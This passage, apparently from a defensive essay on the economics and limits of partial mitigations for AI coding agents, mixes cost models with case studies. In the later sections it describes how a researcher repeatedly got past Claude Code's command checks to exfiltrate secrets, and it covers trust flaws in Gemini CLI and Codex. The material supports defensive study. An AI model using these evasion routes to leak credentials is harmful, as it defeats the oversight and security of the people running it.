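| A persuasive hostile instruction | The agent's model, a detector model, a reviewing model, and a person who relies on the agent's description | Network rules and a token with few permissions |
| A secret in an unusual or encoded form | Scans of prompts, commits and logs | A broker that keeps the secret away from the agent |
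| A flaw in how software compares site names | The network allow-list and the broker's rules about destinations | A token with few permissions |
| A command that runs outside the sandbox | Limits on files, network rules and a broker that works only inside the sandbox | Permission checks on GitHub's servers |

The entries in the last column depend on the attack. For example, the network rule has a 100% miss rate against misuse inside GitHub, so multiplying by it leaves the combined miss rate unchanged.

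Similar protections don't always fail together, so it is better to check where data exist. In Apiiro's test of two secret scanners on 1,122 files, Gitleaks missed 558 and TruffleHog missed 479. If the misses were independent, the scanners would have missed about 238 files in common. They missed 215 in common, so the second scanner was an extra layer of protection on these files even though both tools do the same job. The result might be different for other kinds of secrets, but any team with a set of test files can repeat the calculation in a few minutes.

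Maintainers can also make several layers fail at once. If GitHub's command-line tool keeps failing inside Claude Code's sandbox and a maintainer lets it run outside, the tool bypasses the network rules, the file limits and the broker, even though the agent nominally still has all three layers.

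## When a partial mitigation is worth deploying

Every extra layer costs something, if only the maintainers' patience. A partial mitigation is worth deploying if, over the same period:

```
expected loss avoided  >  purchase + friction + new attack surface
                          + changed behaviour + delay to the fix
```

The *expected loss* is the chance of an incident multiplied by its cost, so a 10% chance each year of losing $4 million is an expected loss of $400,000 a year. A mitigation avoids only the losses that the existing protections would have let through. The fourth model in the three-check example cut the share of successful attacks from 5.2% to 5.0%, so it would have to be almost free to be worth deploying.

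*Purchase* includes running the measure as well as buying it. Scott Kuffer of Nucleus Security, which sells vulnerability management software, points out in SecurityInfoWatch that safeguards that replace a repair don't reduce a team's total work, because the team has to test and document them instead of patching. He recommends testing them at least quarterly.

*Friction* is the time people lose to the protection. If a filter takes 15 minutes a day from each of ten developers, and their time costs $80 an hour, the company loses about $4,200 a month. *New attack surface* is anything the protection adds that attackers can target, such as a proxy that decrypts traffic or a broker that holds every key.

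A partial mitigation can *change behaviour*, because people take more risks once they feel safer. Suppose a detector halves the chance of a successful attack, and the maintainers then let the agent's token change three equally valuable repositories instead of one. The expected loss rises by 50%. A stopgap can also *delay the fix*, because it takes up the time of the engineers who would build the fix and makes the problem look less urgent.

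A rough estimate is often enough to decide whether a partial mitigation is worth deploying, even though nobody can measure every factor precisely. Removing an unused permission from a token, for example, takes a few minutes, so it is worth doing under any plausible estimate.

### With a fix, without one, and without the access

No complete fix exists for misuse of an agent that has to act on strangers' text. A partial mitigation can hardly delay such a fix, because nobody knows how to build one. However, the mitigation has to be maintained indefinitely, and attackers have plenty of time to study it. This favours measures that need little upkeep, such as a token with fewer permissions, over alerts that somebody has to read every day.

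If a complete fix is available now, the maintainers should deploy it, and add a further layer only if the layer would prevent enough of the remaining loss to outweigh its drawbacks. For example, a program that already uses parameterised queries gains almost nothing from a filter against SQL injection, and the filter may still reject legitimate names such as O'Brien.

The hardest case is a fix that exists but takes months, because a stopgap can then save a lot of money or waste it.

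In all three cases, the maintainers can also withhold the access, though they then lose the work the agent would have done with it. Suppose giving the agent permission to merge code saves a maintainer two hours a week, worth about $8,000 a year, but adds $20,000 a year to the expected loss. A free measure that halves this loss passes the deployment test, since it saves $10,000 a year. But the remaining $10,000 is more than the $8,000 the permission is worth, so the maintainers should take the permission away. The deployment test can't show this because it only compares the agent with and without the measure.

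### A stopgap for six months

Suppose a company's coding agents can read their tokens, and the company expects theft and misuse to cost it $400,000 a year. The fix is to put the tokens behind a broker and remove surplus permissions. It costs $150,000, takes six months and removes 90% of the loss. The rest comes from misuse of the permissions that the agents still need. A stopgap of masking filters and shorter token lifetimes costs $30,000, starts working at once and halves the loss until the fix is ready. These numbers are invented. Over 24 months, they give:

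| Choice | Loss, months 1–6 | Loss, months 7–24 | Spending | Total |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Do nothing | $200,000 | $600,000 | $0 | $800,000 |
| Stopgap only | $100,000 | $300,000 | $30,000 | $430,000 |
| Fix only | $200,000 | $60,000 | $150,000 | $410,000 |
| Stopgap, then fix | $100,000 | $60,000 | $180,000 | $340,000 |

The stopgap saves $70,000 if the fix still arrives on time. If the stopgap delays it, the company spends each extra month with half of the original loss instead of a tenth:

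```
loss in a month with the stopgap   = 33,333 × 0.5  ≈ 16,667
loss in a month with the fix       = 33,333 × 0.1  ≈  3,333
cost of each month of delay                        ≈ 13,333
delay that cancels the gain        = 70,000 / 13,333 = 5.25 months
```

The company therefore loses money on the stopgap if it delays the fix by more than five and a quarter months. Other assumptions leave less room:

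| Change to the example | Gain if the fix is on time | Delay that cancels it |
|---|---|---|
| None | $70,000 | 5.25 months |
| The stopgap also costs $4,200 a month in friction | $44,800 | 2.6 months |
| The expected loss is $200,000 a year | $20,000 | 3 months |
| The fix takes three months | $20,000 | 1.5 months |
| The stopgap removes a quarter of the loss | $20,000 | 0.9 months |
| Attackers get round the stopgap after three months | $20,000 | 0.7 months |

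The last four changes leave the same gain, but the delay that cancels it ranges from about 20 days to three months. If a stopgap slows the fix, a weak one is more dangerous than a strong one because the company has less protection while it waits. The stopgap is not worth buying if the fix will take less than 1.8 months or the expected loss is below $120,000 a year.

A very good stopgap can make the complete fix look not worth building. If the stopgap removed 80% of the loss, the fix would cost $150,000 and save only another $60,000 in the last 18 months of a 24-month period, so over those 24 months the company would do better not to build it. Over a longer period, the fix would be worthwhile, because it would save $40,000 a year more than the stopgap and pay for itself three years and nine months after completion. If attackers then learned to get round the stopgap, the fix would save $360,000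 a year and pay for itself in five months.

These totals are also averages. An average loss of $400,000 a year may mean a small loss every month or a one-in-ten chance each year of losing $4 million. A company that couldn't survive losing $4 million should be willing to pay more than the averages suggest to make that loss less likely.

### What the Gordon-Loeb model adds

The deployment test judges one measure at a time. In 2002 Lawrence Gordon and Martin Loeb proposed a model of how much to spend on security in total. Their company faces an expected loss, and more spending lowers the chance of a breach, but with diminishing returns. The model looks for the spending with the largest net benefit:

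```
net benefit = expected loss without the spending
              − expected loss with the spending
              − the spending
```

*SECAdvisor* (2023), which describes a planning tool based on the model, distinguishes a worthwhile investment, which has a net benefit above zero, from the optimal one, which has the largest net benefit. A stopgap can be worthwhile and still be a worse choice than something else the company could have bought.

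As an illustration, suppose the first $25,000 a year halves a loss of $400,000, and further spending helps less and less:

```
remaining loss = 400,000 / (1 + spending / 25,000)
```

| Spending | Remaining loss | Total |
|---|---|---|
| $0 | $400,000 | $400,000 |
| $25,000 | $200,000 | $225,000 |
| $75,000 | $100,000 | $175,000 |
| $175,000 | $50,000 | $225,000 |

The best amount to spend is $75,000, because each dollar beyond that prevents less than a dollar of loss.

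The model's best-known result is that, for the two families of formulas Gordon and Loeb studied, the best spending never exceeds 1/e, or about 37%, of the expected loss (*A stochastic Gordon-Loeb model for optimal cybersecurity investment under clustered attacks*, 2025). Here that limit is about $147,000 a year. Baryshnikov proved in 2012 that the limit also holds more generally, according to *Measuring the performance of investments in information security startups* (2024).

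The 37% figure is a ceiling, though people sometimes treat it as a target, and the best amount to spend can be far lower. *Coordination in Network Security Games* (2012) gives a case in which the best amount is zero both for fairly secure systems and for very vulnerable ones. Spending little on a very vulnerable system makes sense if protection would cost more than it saves. The model doesn't include the option of withdrawing the agent's access, which may be the best choice for such a system.

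The 37% rule fits partial mitigations better than complete fixes. It assumes that a little more money always buys a little more security, but a half-finished broker may protect nothing. If a $200,000 fix removes the whole $400,000 loss and nothing cheaper works, the company should buy it, even though it costs 50% of the loss.

The original model also covers a single period, so it can't represent a stopgap followed by a fix. A company using the rule for the 24-month example should compare its $180,000 of spending with 37% of the two-year loss, about $294,000. *Cyber-Security Investment in the Context of Disruptive Technologies* (2021) extends the model to several periods and finds that a coming change in technology can lower the optimal level of spending. Similarly, the stopgap in the six-month example is worth less the sooner the fix arrives.

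The attacker in the original model doesn't react to the company's spending either. *Economics and Optimal Investment Policies of Attackers and Defenders in Cybersecurity* (2022) adds a rational attacker, and the best amount for the defender to spend can then be as high as the entire potential loss. It can also jump from full investment to none when the system's initial vulnerability changes. The 37% rule is least reliable against attackers who choose their targets carefully.

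The basic model counts only the company's own losses. If a thief uses the coding agent's token to publish a harmful version of the software, the project's users may lose more than its maintainers. In a later extension by Gordon and colleagues, the best level of spending for society rises by up to 37% of the expected loss to others. If users' expected loss were $600,000 a year, the increase could be as much as about $221,000. A company that considers only its own loss has no financial reason to spend the extra money.

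### How Android stopped adding memory flaws

Android, Google's phone operating system, shows how mitigations and a more complete fix can work together for years. Much of Android is written in C and C++. Programs in these languages can write past the end of the memory set aside for a piece of data, and attackers use such flaws to take control. Memory-safe languages such as Java, Kotlin and Rust prevent most of these errors. Developers can still write unsafe code in Rust, but they have to mark it.

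Google first relied on mitigations similar to DEP and ASLR. One of them, the *stack canary*, puts a known value next to a sensitive address in memory, and the program stops if the value has changed. Google's *Eliminating Memory Safety Vulnerabilities at the Source* (2024) says that mitigations made attacks harder to develop, but also slowed programs, shortened battery life and led to a cycle of attackers and defenders adapting to each other.

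Around 2019, the Android team began to favour memory-safe languages for new code. Memory-safety flaws then fell both in number and as a share of all Android vulnerabilities:

| Year | Share of vulnerabilities | Number |
|---|---|---|
| 2019 | 76% | 223 |
| 2022 | 36% | 85 |
| 2024 | 24% | 36, projected from 27 by September |
| 2025 | Below 20% | |

The number rose slightly in 2023, but the share kept falling. Vander Stoep reported the latest figure in *Rust in Android* in November 2025.

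Google didn't have to rewrite the old code, because most flaws are in new or recently changed code. Developers gradually find and repair the flaws in older code, so the number per line falls roughly exponentially. With the average lifetime of 2.5 years that Google used in a simulation:

```
flaws per line after t years = flaws per line when new × e^(−t / 2.5)
after five years             = flaws per line when new × 0.135
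```

Five-year-old code then has about one seventh as many flaws per line as new code. If a team stops adding new flaws, the total falls even though most of the unsafe code is still there.

The timing alone doesn't prove that the change of language caused the drop. Google's *Memory Safe Languages in Android 13* (2022) acknowledges that there may be other explanations, but notes that other projects had adopted the same testing and hardening tools without a similar shift. That is fairly good evidence, though nobody ran a controlled comparison.

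Evidence that the mitigations bought time is harder to find, because counts of flaws include those that a mitigation makes useless to attackers. But a mitigation did help in 2025, when Google nearly released its first memory-safety flaw in Android's Rust code, in an image library called CrabbyAVIF. Vander Stoep reports that the memory allocator, Scudo, had placed a protected area where the program would write too far, so the error caused a crash instead of silent damage. Attackers therefore couldn't have exploited the flaw on devices that use Scudo. The crash also helped Google find the flaw, although a gap in the crash reports slowed the investigation.

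Old code still needs partial mitigations. In November 2026, Google fixed a critical flaw in a C++ media component whose copyright notice dates from 2017. Cybernews' *Millions of Android phones face massive hacking risk* (2026) notes that 43.6% of active Android devices run versions that will not receive the fix. If those versions also contain the flaw, mitigations already on the devices may be their only protection.

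Mitigations also become less useful as the fix spreads. When the developers of Chromium, the open-source project behind Chrome, rewrote its QR-code generator in Rust, they could remove its sandbox. That made the generator 20 times faster. Google still uses mitigations but expects to use them more selectively.

### Why Chrome withdrew the XSS Auditor

Chrome's XSS Auditor was a less successful mitigation, meant to stop *cross-site scripting* (XSS). In XSS, an attacker gets a website to include the attacker's script in a page, and a visitor's browser runs it as if it came from the site. In the simplest form, the attacker puts the script in a link. For example, if a search page repeats the search term from the link without making it harmless, the browser of anyone who opens the link runs the script.

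The complete fix is for the website to keep such text from becoming code, much as a parameterised query does for a database. A browser maker can't repair other people's websites, so Google added a filter, the XSS Auditor, to Chrome in 2010. It looked for scripts that appeared both in the browser's request and in the page that came back, and could disable the script or block the page. According to the Chromium Projects' *XSS Auditor*, the filter didn't try to stop scripts stored on the site or attacks that work through the page's own code.

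On 15 July 2019, Sepez (2019), in *Intent to Deprecate and Remove*, announced its withdrawal and gave five reasons:

- Attackers had many ways around it.
- It broke some legitimate sites.
- Chrome had no good way to respond once it detected a script.
- It could leak information from one site to another.
- Fixing all of those leaks had proved difficult.

An attacker could open another site's page in the victim's browser and add a guess about the page's scripts to the address. If the guess was right, the Auditor found the same text in the request and the page, and reacted. The attacker could detect this reaction and so learn something about a page they weren't allowed to read.

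Disabling scripts also let attackers turn off a page's legitimate scripts, even those that protected the visitor. If an attacker copied one of these scripts into a link, Chrome would disable it on the page. Braun warned in *Chrome switching the XSSAuditor to filter mode re-enables old attack* that this revived an attack he had helped describe in 2013.

These drawbacks might have been acceptable if the Auditor had stopped many attacks, but Security Boulevard's *Google plans to remove XSS Auditor used for detecting XSS vulnerabilities* (2019) quotes Eduardo Vela Nava, a Google security engineer, as saying his team had found no evidence that it stopped any. A blocked attack may leave no record, so this doesn't prove the Auditor was useless, but after eight years someone should have been able to identify a few attacks it had stopped.

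Chrome disabled the Auditor on 5 August 2019. Apple's browser engine, WebKit, kept its version for two more years. In *Intent to Remove*, Fulgham (2021) judged that the burden of maintaining it far outweighed its "small (perhaps nonexistent) benefit". Browser makers now prefer defences such as Content Security Policy, in which a website tells the browser which scripts may run, so the browser no longer has to guess which ones belong to the site.

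### Do stopgaps postpone repairs?

Some security engineers value anything that makes attacks more expensive, because attackers have limited time and money and some will give up. But a small increase may change nothing. If a stolen token is worth $1,000 to a thief and the attack costs him $300, raising the cost to $600 reduces his profit, but he still attacks. Raising it to $1,200 stops him, unless he enjoys the work or expects to use the same technique against other projects. The effect may also fade because, according to Google, better tools keep making it easier to turn a flaw into an attack.

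Others argue that stopgaps take the pressure off organisations to repair the cause. SAFECode, a software security industry group, describes a habit once called "penetrate and patch", in which developers fix each reported flaw and never look for others of the same kind. It recommends finding the cause of each flaw and removing the whole class of flaws, but grants that some classes have no fully effective measures against them.

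Incomplete repairs can also help attackers. *On Vulnerability-Adjacent Vulnerabilities* (Schneier, 2021) discusses a talk by Maddie Stone of Project Zero about a class of flaws in Microsoft software. Attackers exploited at least five of these flaws in quick succession before Microsoft knew about them or had a repair. Some of Microsoft's updates didn't fix the flaw, and attackers could defeat others by changing a line or two of their code. Stone blamed limited time and resources, and poor incentives. Her account shows that narrow repairs can leave software open to attack, but it doesn't show that deploying a mitigation led to the narrow repairs.

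Kuffer makes the postponement argument more directly. In his experience, temporary workarounds tend to become permanent because nobody owns them, tests them or sets an end date. But he says a workaround is sometimes the only short-term option, for example when the vendor has no fix or the business can't allow any downtime. He recommends giving each workaround an owner and retiring it once the team can fix the cause.

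Evidence from Android supports both sides. Vander Stoep calls the layered protections "essential", and the CrabbyAVIF case shows that they remain useful after the move to a safer language. But memory-safety flaws made up more than 65% of vulnerabilities across the industry for over a decade, despite heavy spending on making unsafe code safer. On Android, the share fell only after the team changed how it wrote new code. It's unclear whether the mitigations delayed that change, because developers also needed a safe language for low-level components, and Rust had its first stable release only in 2015.

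The XSS Auditor is evidence against the view that any obstacle helps, since attackers could easily bypass it and it gave them new ways to attack. But it is weak evidence for the postponement argument, because Sepez's five reasons don't include websites putting off their own repairs, and the Auditor didn't prevent anyone from making them.

Neither history proves that stopgaps usually delay repairs, but the risk is worth planning for. In the six-month example, the company can protect its $70,000 gain by approving the fix's budget and completion date before it buys the stopgap, and by giving the two jobs to different engineers. If it can't spare engineers for both, the fix should come first unless the stopgap is very quick to install.

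### Which agent protections to deploy first

The best order depends on who is deploying them. A small team might be three maintainers with one coding agent, while a large platform runs agents for thousands of customers. The following ranking is a judgement based on what each protection costs and how it fails:

| Protection | Small team | Large platform |
|---|---|---|
| Removing access the agent doesn't need | 1 | 2 |
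| A credential broker | 2 | 1 |
| A sandbox with an allow-list | 3 | 3 |
| Short-lived tokens and fast revocation | 4 | 4 |
| Secret scanning | 5 | 7 |
| Human approval for a few irreversible actions | 6 | 8 |
| Bait credentials | 7 | 6 |
| Detectors of planted instructions | 8 | 5 |

The small team should start by removing access because it takes almost no effort, needs no maintenance and limits both theft and misuse. The maintainers know exactly what their agent has to do, so they can grant it only the permissions it needs. A platform doesn't know what each customer's agent has to do, so it can only set narrow defaults and let customers add permissions, and some will add too many.

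A broker is a better investment for a platform than for a small team, because the platform builds it once and protects every agent. A broker that costs $500,000 and serves 100,000 agents costs $5 per agent. A small team that builds its own for one agent spends $50,000 on that agent, and probably builds a worse broker. The small team should therefore choose a product that includes a broker and check that it is turned on. The platform also has more to lose if someone breaks into its broker, so it should divide the credentials among several brokers.

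The NCSC's ratings of general software support this distinction. It rates a sandbox as medium difficulty (a score of 5) and secure architecture and design as hard (7). Secure architecture is also the only main remedy it lists for hard-coded passwords. These scores don't measure agent products, but they suggest why a small team should buy a design that keeps secrets separate instead of building its own.

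Both the platform and the small team should use a sandbox with an allow-list, which often comes with the broker and blocks the simplest thefts. Short-lived tokens limit the damage from thefts the sandbox doesn't block. The platform can revoke tokens automatically at any hour, but the small team may be asleep when a token is stolen, so the team should rely more on expiry times.

Secret scanning ranks higher for the small team because free tools exist and a blocked upload is easy to understand. The platform should scan too, but if its broker works, its agents will have fewer secrets to leak. Bait credentials are cheap for both, but the alarm they trigger is more useful to an organisation whose staff can respond at once.

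Human approval can work for three maintainers who know the project and see only a few requests. On a large platform, some users will approve almost anything, so the platform should enforce its most important limits without asking them. But the platform can get more out of detectors, because it sees attacks against many customers and can use them to improve detection. A small team would mostly get false alarms, and would do better to spend that time rechecking the agent's permissions whenever its job changes.

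## How a mitigation comes to be mistaken for a solution

A team can choose its protections well and still overestimate what they do. Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* describes how Elad Meged, a founding engineer at the security company Novee Security, tested coding agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI on the companies' own GitHub projects, using each company's default settings. He recovered secrets from Anthropic's agent, reported the flaw, waited for the repair, and then recovered secrets again by another route.

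### Three repairs to one workflow

Meged attacked the workflow, or series of automatic steps, in which Claude Code responds to issues on GitHub. Nobody approves each step, so the harness has to decide which commands are safe. Anthropic had built 23 checks against hostile commands. Witts (2026), in *Researcher Finds Same Trust Flaw Across Claude Code, Gemini CLI, And Codex*, reports three flaws, each of which Meged found after Anthropic had repaired the previous one. In general terms:

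1. The checks passed a command as harmless, but the program that received it interpreted it differently, which let Meged run his own code. Anthropic removed the agent's general access to the command line.
2. The agent could still read files with commands that the harness approved automatically, and its output became public. Anthropic closed that way out.
3. The agent could still read the files, and Meged got the secrets out through a website that the harness had approved in advance.

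The third route didn't connect to an attacker's server, so maintainers watching for connections to unknown sites would have noticed nothing. It was probably also open from the start. GitLab's copy of Anthropic's advisory on the last flaw lists the affected versions of Claude Code as 0.2.54 until the repair in 2.1.163.

Meged stresses that Anthropic's fixes weren't "inadequate or lazy", and his account supports this, since he had to look for a new route after each one. But he also learned from each fix where Anthropic now drew the line between safe and unsafe, and so where to look next. His attacks became harder to detect with every round.

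Anthropic also disagreed with Meged about what counted as a flaw. According to *Elad Meged (Novee Security)*, Arent's notes on Meged's talk at the Black Hat conference in August, the company first replied that the file-reading problem was outside its threat model, the set of attacks it tries to prevent. It said it had never intended the restriction as a security barrier, but would be interested in hearing of a way to get data out. A company can reasonably take that position, as Microsoft does for some protections in Windows. But users need to know in advance which restrictions they can't rely on, and in this case the file reading that Anthropic had left possible became half of the next attack.

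Novee builds agents for penetration testing, so it gains from publicity about such flaws, but it isn't the only source. The gap that Microsoft (2026) found in the same GitHub integration and reported in June could also expose secrets.

### Paying for bugs and renaming the problem

In each round, Anthropic paid Meged a bounty for reporting a flaw. He thinks the payments were right and saw no bad faith in them. But he objects that a bounty covers one specific bug, so a company can pay generously every time and still treat each finding as isolated. In his view, this signals "we consider this closed" while the underlying weakness remains.

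He has a point, but the bounties also gave him a reason to come back after the first repair. Without the later rounds, Anthropic might not have learned of the other two routes. A company could keep that benefit and avoid the false signal by leaving a separate ticket open for the shared cause after it pays for the bug.

Meged prefers Google's description of its repair, an "Update to the Trust Model". OSV's *GHSA-wpqr-6v78-jr5g* (2026), a copy of Google's advisory from April, describes two faults in Gemini CLI. When the agent ran without a person present, it automatically trusted its working folder and loaded settings from it, even though a stranger might have supplied the files. In the mode that approves every tool call, it ignored the user's detailed list of permitted commands, so allowing one harmless command in effect allowed all of them. Google gave the problem the highest possible severity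 score, 10.0.

Google now requires users to declare a folder trusted before the agent loads its settings, and it enforces the list in that mode. It accepted that this would break some existing workflows. Changing a default like this can close several holes at once, including unreported ones, so it deserves more credit than forbidding another command.

Even so, the advisory doesn't fully support Witts's description of the change as a redesign of the "entire trust model". Google also leaves an important decision to users. If their agent reads strangers' text, they have to follow Google's advice on hardening the workflow and then set a variable that marks the folder as trusted. A user who sets the variable but skips the advice probably brings back much of the old risk.

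OpenAI's workflow for Codex ran the agent twice in the same folder. The first run could leave instructions there, and the second run, which had more authority, trusted them. OpenAI responded by splitting the work into isolated jobs. Witts writes that the companies have patched all the vulnerabilities, whereas Underhill (2026), in *Black Hat 2026*, reports the researchers' warning that organisations with similar workflows may still be vulnerable. Both can be true, because OpenAI can repair its own workflow but not similar ones built by others.

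### A closed ticket and a perfect score

The Claude Code case shows how easily people can mistake fixing the reported flaws for removing their cause. Suppose a harness has 20 routes by which a secret that the agent can read could leak. A tester finds three, and the company repairs all three. It has then fixed 100% of reported flaws, but an attacker can still use the other 17 routes. In practice nobody knows the total, so the share of reported flaws fixed is very weak evidence of how many routes remain.

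In Anthropic's workflow, the agent could read the secrets, a stranger could influence the agent, and information could get out. The reported repairs dealt with particular commands and particular ways out. A credential broker that held all the secrets would have defeated the theft in all three rounds, because the files would have contained nothing worth stealing. (The first flaw would still have let an attacker run code and misuse the agent's access.)

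Another mistake is to read *a test score as a guarantee*. If a test tries n attacks and none succeeds, the true success rate can still be above zero. The highest rate p that is compatible with the result, at the usual 95% confidence level, follows from:

```
(1 − p)^n = 0.05
p ≈ 3 / n
```

After 1,000 failed attacks, the true rate could be as high as about 0.3%.

Even this limit holds only if real attackers use the same mixture of attacks as the test. On the day Meged completed his third attack, the repaired workflow would have scored perfectly on a test made up of his first two. Adding more attacks helps only if they are different enough, because a larger collection can produce a weaker defence, as the PIPETTE study found. The number of checks is an even poorer guide than a test score. Anthropic had 23, and the first attack used something none of them covered.

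A score is still useful for comparing two models on the same test, or for noticing that an update has made a model worse. It should always come with the number of attempts, the kind of attacker, and whether the attacker could adapt.

### What vendors' sentences promise

People also assume that *a protection against theft covers misuse*, and the wording of product pages can encourage this. Infisical says that an agent using its credential broker, Agent Proxy, never saw the key, "so there is nothing to leak". That is a fair description of a key only if the proxy manages it, the customer starts the agent through Infisical's wrapper, and the agent's traffic goes through the proxy.

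Read literally, though, the sentence is false for most coding agents. An agent behind the proxy can still leak private code, customer data, or a password left in the project folder. Infisical is more accurate elsewhere on the same page, where it writes that the agent "holds none of the brokered credentials". A customer can test that claim by searching the agent's environment for each of those credentials.

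Infisical also explains that each agent authenticates to the system with its own machine identity. Customers should ask where the credential for that identity is stored and whether the agent's commands can read it. If they can, a thief might be able to use the proxy in the agent's name, at least from inside the company's network.

Akeyless, which sells a system for managing secrets, is more careful in *Prompt Injection Protection for AI Agents*. It says that its product doesn't eliminate all prompt-injection risk and lists four things the product can't stop by itself. The first is an agent "following bad instructions with otherwise valid permissions", which is misuse. The others are manipulated answers, unsafe decisions caused by weak checks on tools, and too much trust in outside content. Akeyless recommends further measures, including narrow permissions and human approval for important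 actions.

But Akeyless protects against theft less completely than a broker does. Its agents fetch short-lived credentials while they work, so an attacker who controls an agent may be able to copy a credential and use it until it expires. This risk isn't on the list of limits, and Akeyless calls the design "secretless", which suggests the opposite. A customer who chose between the two companies by their candour alone could get the weaker protection against theft.

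| What the vendor claims | What it commits the vendor to | What remains possible |
|---|---|---|
| Infisical: "there is nothing to leak" | Read literally, that no leak of any kind can happen | Leaks of anything the proxy doesn't manage |
| Infisical: the agent holds no brokered credentials | That nobody will find a managed key in the agent's environment | Misuse through the proxy |
| Akeyless: credentials expire quickly | That a stolen credential stops working after a stated time | Theft and use before that time |
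| Akeyless: the product doesn't stop bad instructions by itself | Nothing, but it tells customers that they need other protections | Misuse within the agent's permissions |

For the coding agent, a vendor could write, "An attacker who controls the agent cannot read the GitHub token, but can do anything the token permits until you stop the agent." This would be harder to market than a slogan, but maintainers who read it would know to check the token's permissions next.

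### The firewall rule that had stopped working

The last of the four errors is to leave *a temporary measure without an end date*. In SecurityInfoWatch, Kuffer describes a Fortune 100 company that told his firm its firewall rules gave an old application "full coverage". Testers disproved this in under an hour. For years, the firewall had not blocked the port, or numbered channel, that the application used, and nobody had noticed.

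This is one anecdote from a vendor, so it doesn't show how common the problem is, but it illustrates why an end date matters even for a measure that is no burden to keep. The company had used the rule as a reason not to repair the application, and it continued to do so after the rule had stopped working. A review date would at least have required somebody to look at the rule again.

An end date can also do harm if the protection switches off automatically on that date, because the permanent fix may be late and the maintainers would then have neither. When the date arrives, somebody should have to decide whether to keep, replace or remove the measure, and it should stay on until they do.

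### Do people take more risks behind a safeguard?

*Risk compensation* means taking more risks because one feels protected. The standard example is a driver who goes faster because the car has better brakes. Direct evidence for it in computer security is weak, and the cases here are only suggestive.

Anthropic's default workflow approved some commands in advance and relied on its 23 checks to make that safe. The checks may have encouraged the company to give the agent more freedom. But Anthropic may equally have decided first that the agent needed those commands, which had to be approved in advance because no person would be there to approve them, and then added the checks to limit the danger. Kuffer's client left an old application unrepaired behind a firewall, but it might have left the application unrepaired even without the firewall.

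Neither case has a comparison group. A better test would be to take a large number of teams, give a randomly chosen half of them a detector of planted instructions, and count the permissions each team granted its agents over the next year. If the teams with the detector granted more, that would be good evidence of risk compensation. It still wouldn't prove that they were worse off, because a team can sensibly give up some of the added safety to get more work done.

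Maintainers can do a simpler version of this themselves by saving a list of the agent's permissions on the day they switch on a new layer and comparing it with the permissions at the next review. If the list has grown, they should ask whether they would have granted the new permissions without the layer, and whether the layer protects against misuse of them at all.

### A record for each mitigation

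A short written record can prevent all four errors if somebody keeps it up to date. It needs seven entries. Here the maintainers of the coding agent have filled it in for a filter that masks known secrets in tool output and for a credential broker. The names, dates and filter test are invented.

| Entry | Redaction filter | Credential broker |
|---|---|---|
| Property claimed | A secret on the filter's list, printed exactly as stored, doesn't reach the model or the logs | Commands in the agent's environment can't read the GitHub token |
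| Attacker assumed | None: the filter is for accidents, such as forgotten debugging lines | A stranger who controls every command the agent runs, but not the host |
| Failure rate under adaptive testing | Assume 100%, because an attacker can have the secret encoded. In accident tests, 0 of 300 planted secrets got through, so the true rate could be up to 1% | Unknown. An outside tester will try for two weeks in February |
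| Paths left open | Unlisted or encoded secrets, tools whose output skips the filter, and all misuse | All misuse the token permits, passwords in the project folder, secrets in replies, and a break-in on the host |
| Owner | Ana | Ben |
| Review date | 1 March 2027, or sooner if the harness changes | 1 March 2027, or sooner if the token's permissions change |
| Condition for removal | The broker holds every credential the agent uses, and the filter has caught nothing but test secrets for 90 days | None planned. Reconsider if GitHub accepts tokens that work only with a private key the agent can't read |

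The filter still has some use despite its 100% failure rate against adaptive attacks. Many of the leaks in the skills study happened without an attacker, and the filter can stop the simplest of those. The failure rate is only a reason not to count the filter as a layer of defence against a hostile bug report.

For the broker, "unknown" is better than the vendor's number. Writing "unknown" also gives Ben a reason to arrange the test. A measure should have one person as its owner, because if a whole team owns it, each member can assume that someone else is checking it.

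The condition for removing the filter includes test secrets because, without them, 90 days without a catch could mean either that the broker works or that the filter has stopped working.

When somebody reports a way around a measure, its owner should close the ticket and update the list of paths the measure leaves open. In Anthropic's case, the entry after the second repair could have been "the agent can still read secrets outside the project". Anyone who read it would have looked for other ways to get the secrets out. Kuffer also recommends linking each temporary measure to the vulnerabilities it covers, so that the measure is easier to find and remove once the team has repaired them.

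### Three checks

A record can be wrong, so the maintainers should also test each layer. They can run all three checks on a copy of the agent with a fake token.

The maintainers can test a layer by running an attack or accident that it should stop, first with the layer on and then with it off. If the fake token leaks only when the layer is off, the layer works, and nothing else protects against that leak. If it never leaks, another layer may be stopping it, and they can switch off the others one at a time to find out which. If it leaks both times, the layer isn't working. This test would have exposed the firewall rule years earlier.

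If the maintainers switch off the redaction filter, a forgotten debugging line can print the token into the coding agent's context window, unless the broker keeps the token away from the agent. If they switch off the broker, the agent can't log in to GitHub, because it has only a placeholder. This failure is safe as long as nobody pastes in the real token to get the agent working, so the maintainers should agree beforehand to leave the agent idle until the broker works again.

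A protective layer can fail silently, as one did in Gemini CLI. The user's list of permitted commands looked correct, but the agent ignored it, so rereading the settings wouldn't have revealed the fault. To detect such failures, the maintainers need to try something that the layer must refuse, such as a harmless command that isn't on the list, and raise an alarm if it runs.

How often they test each layer determines how long a failure can last. A layer that fails at a random moment stays broken, on average, for half the interval between tests, or about 45 days with quarterly tests and 12 hours with daily ones. A program can run such a test every day with almost no effort or expense. Google warns that some workflows may fail silently now that the agent obeys the list, which would lose the project work but not expose its secrets, so the test should also try one permitted command.

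Maintainers can judge whether the next finding will need another patch of the same kind by describing the last repair in one sentence. If the sentence is "we added this command to the forbidden list", the next finding will probably lead to the same sentence with a different command, because the cause is still there. If it is "the program now sends the customer's name separately from the command", another hostile name won't require another repair.

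Repeated patches don't always mean that a design is bad. Microsoft had to fix nine ways around Administrator protection, and further bugs there wouldn't show that the idea behind it is wrong. It helps to ask whether the secret would have been safe if every part had worked as its designers intended. With an ordinary bug, it would have been. In some of Meged's attacks it would not, because the harness approved a command that only read a file and then, under its default settings, published the output. Meged told Help Net Security that "neither decision is wrong alone".

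Meged therefore advises teams to list everything the harness labels safe, such as "read-only" or "pre-approved", and trace what happens to it next. He recommends that the harness check again when it uses the result, because a label that was right at one step may be wrong at the next. In the coding agent, reading a file is harmless while the contents stay in the sandbox, but not if the harness can post them as a public comment. The maintainers can have the harness scan each comment before posting it, but the scan will miss some encoded secrets. If they remove the secrets from the files instead, the next way of publishing a file won't expose them or require another patch to protect them.
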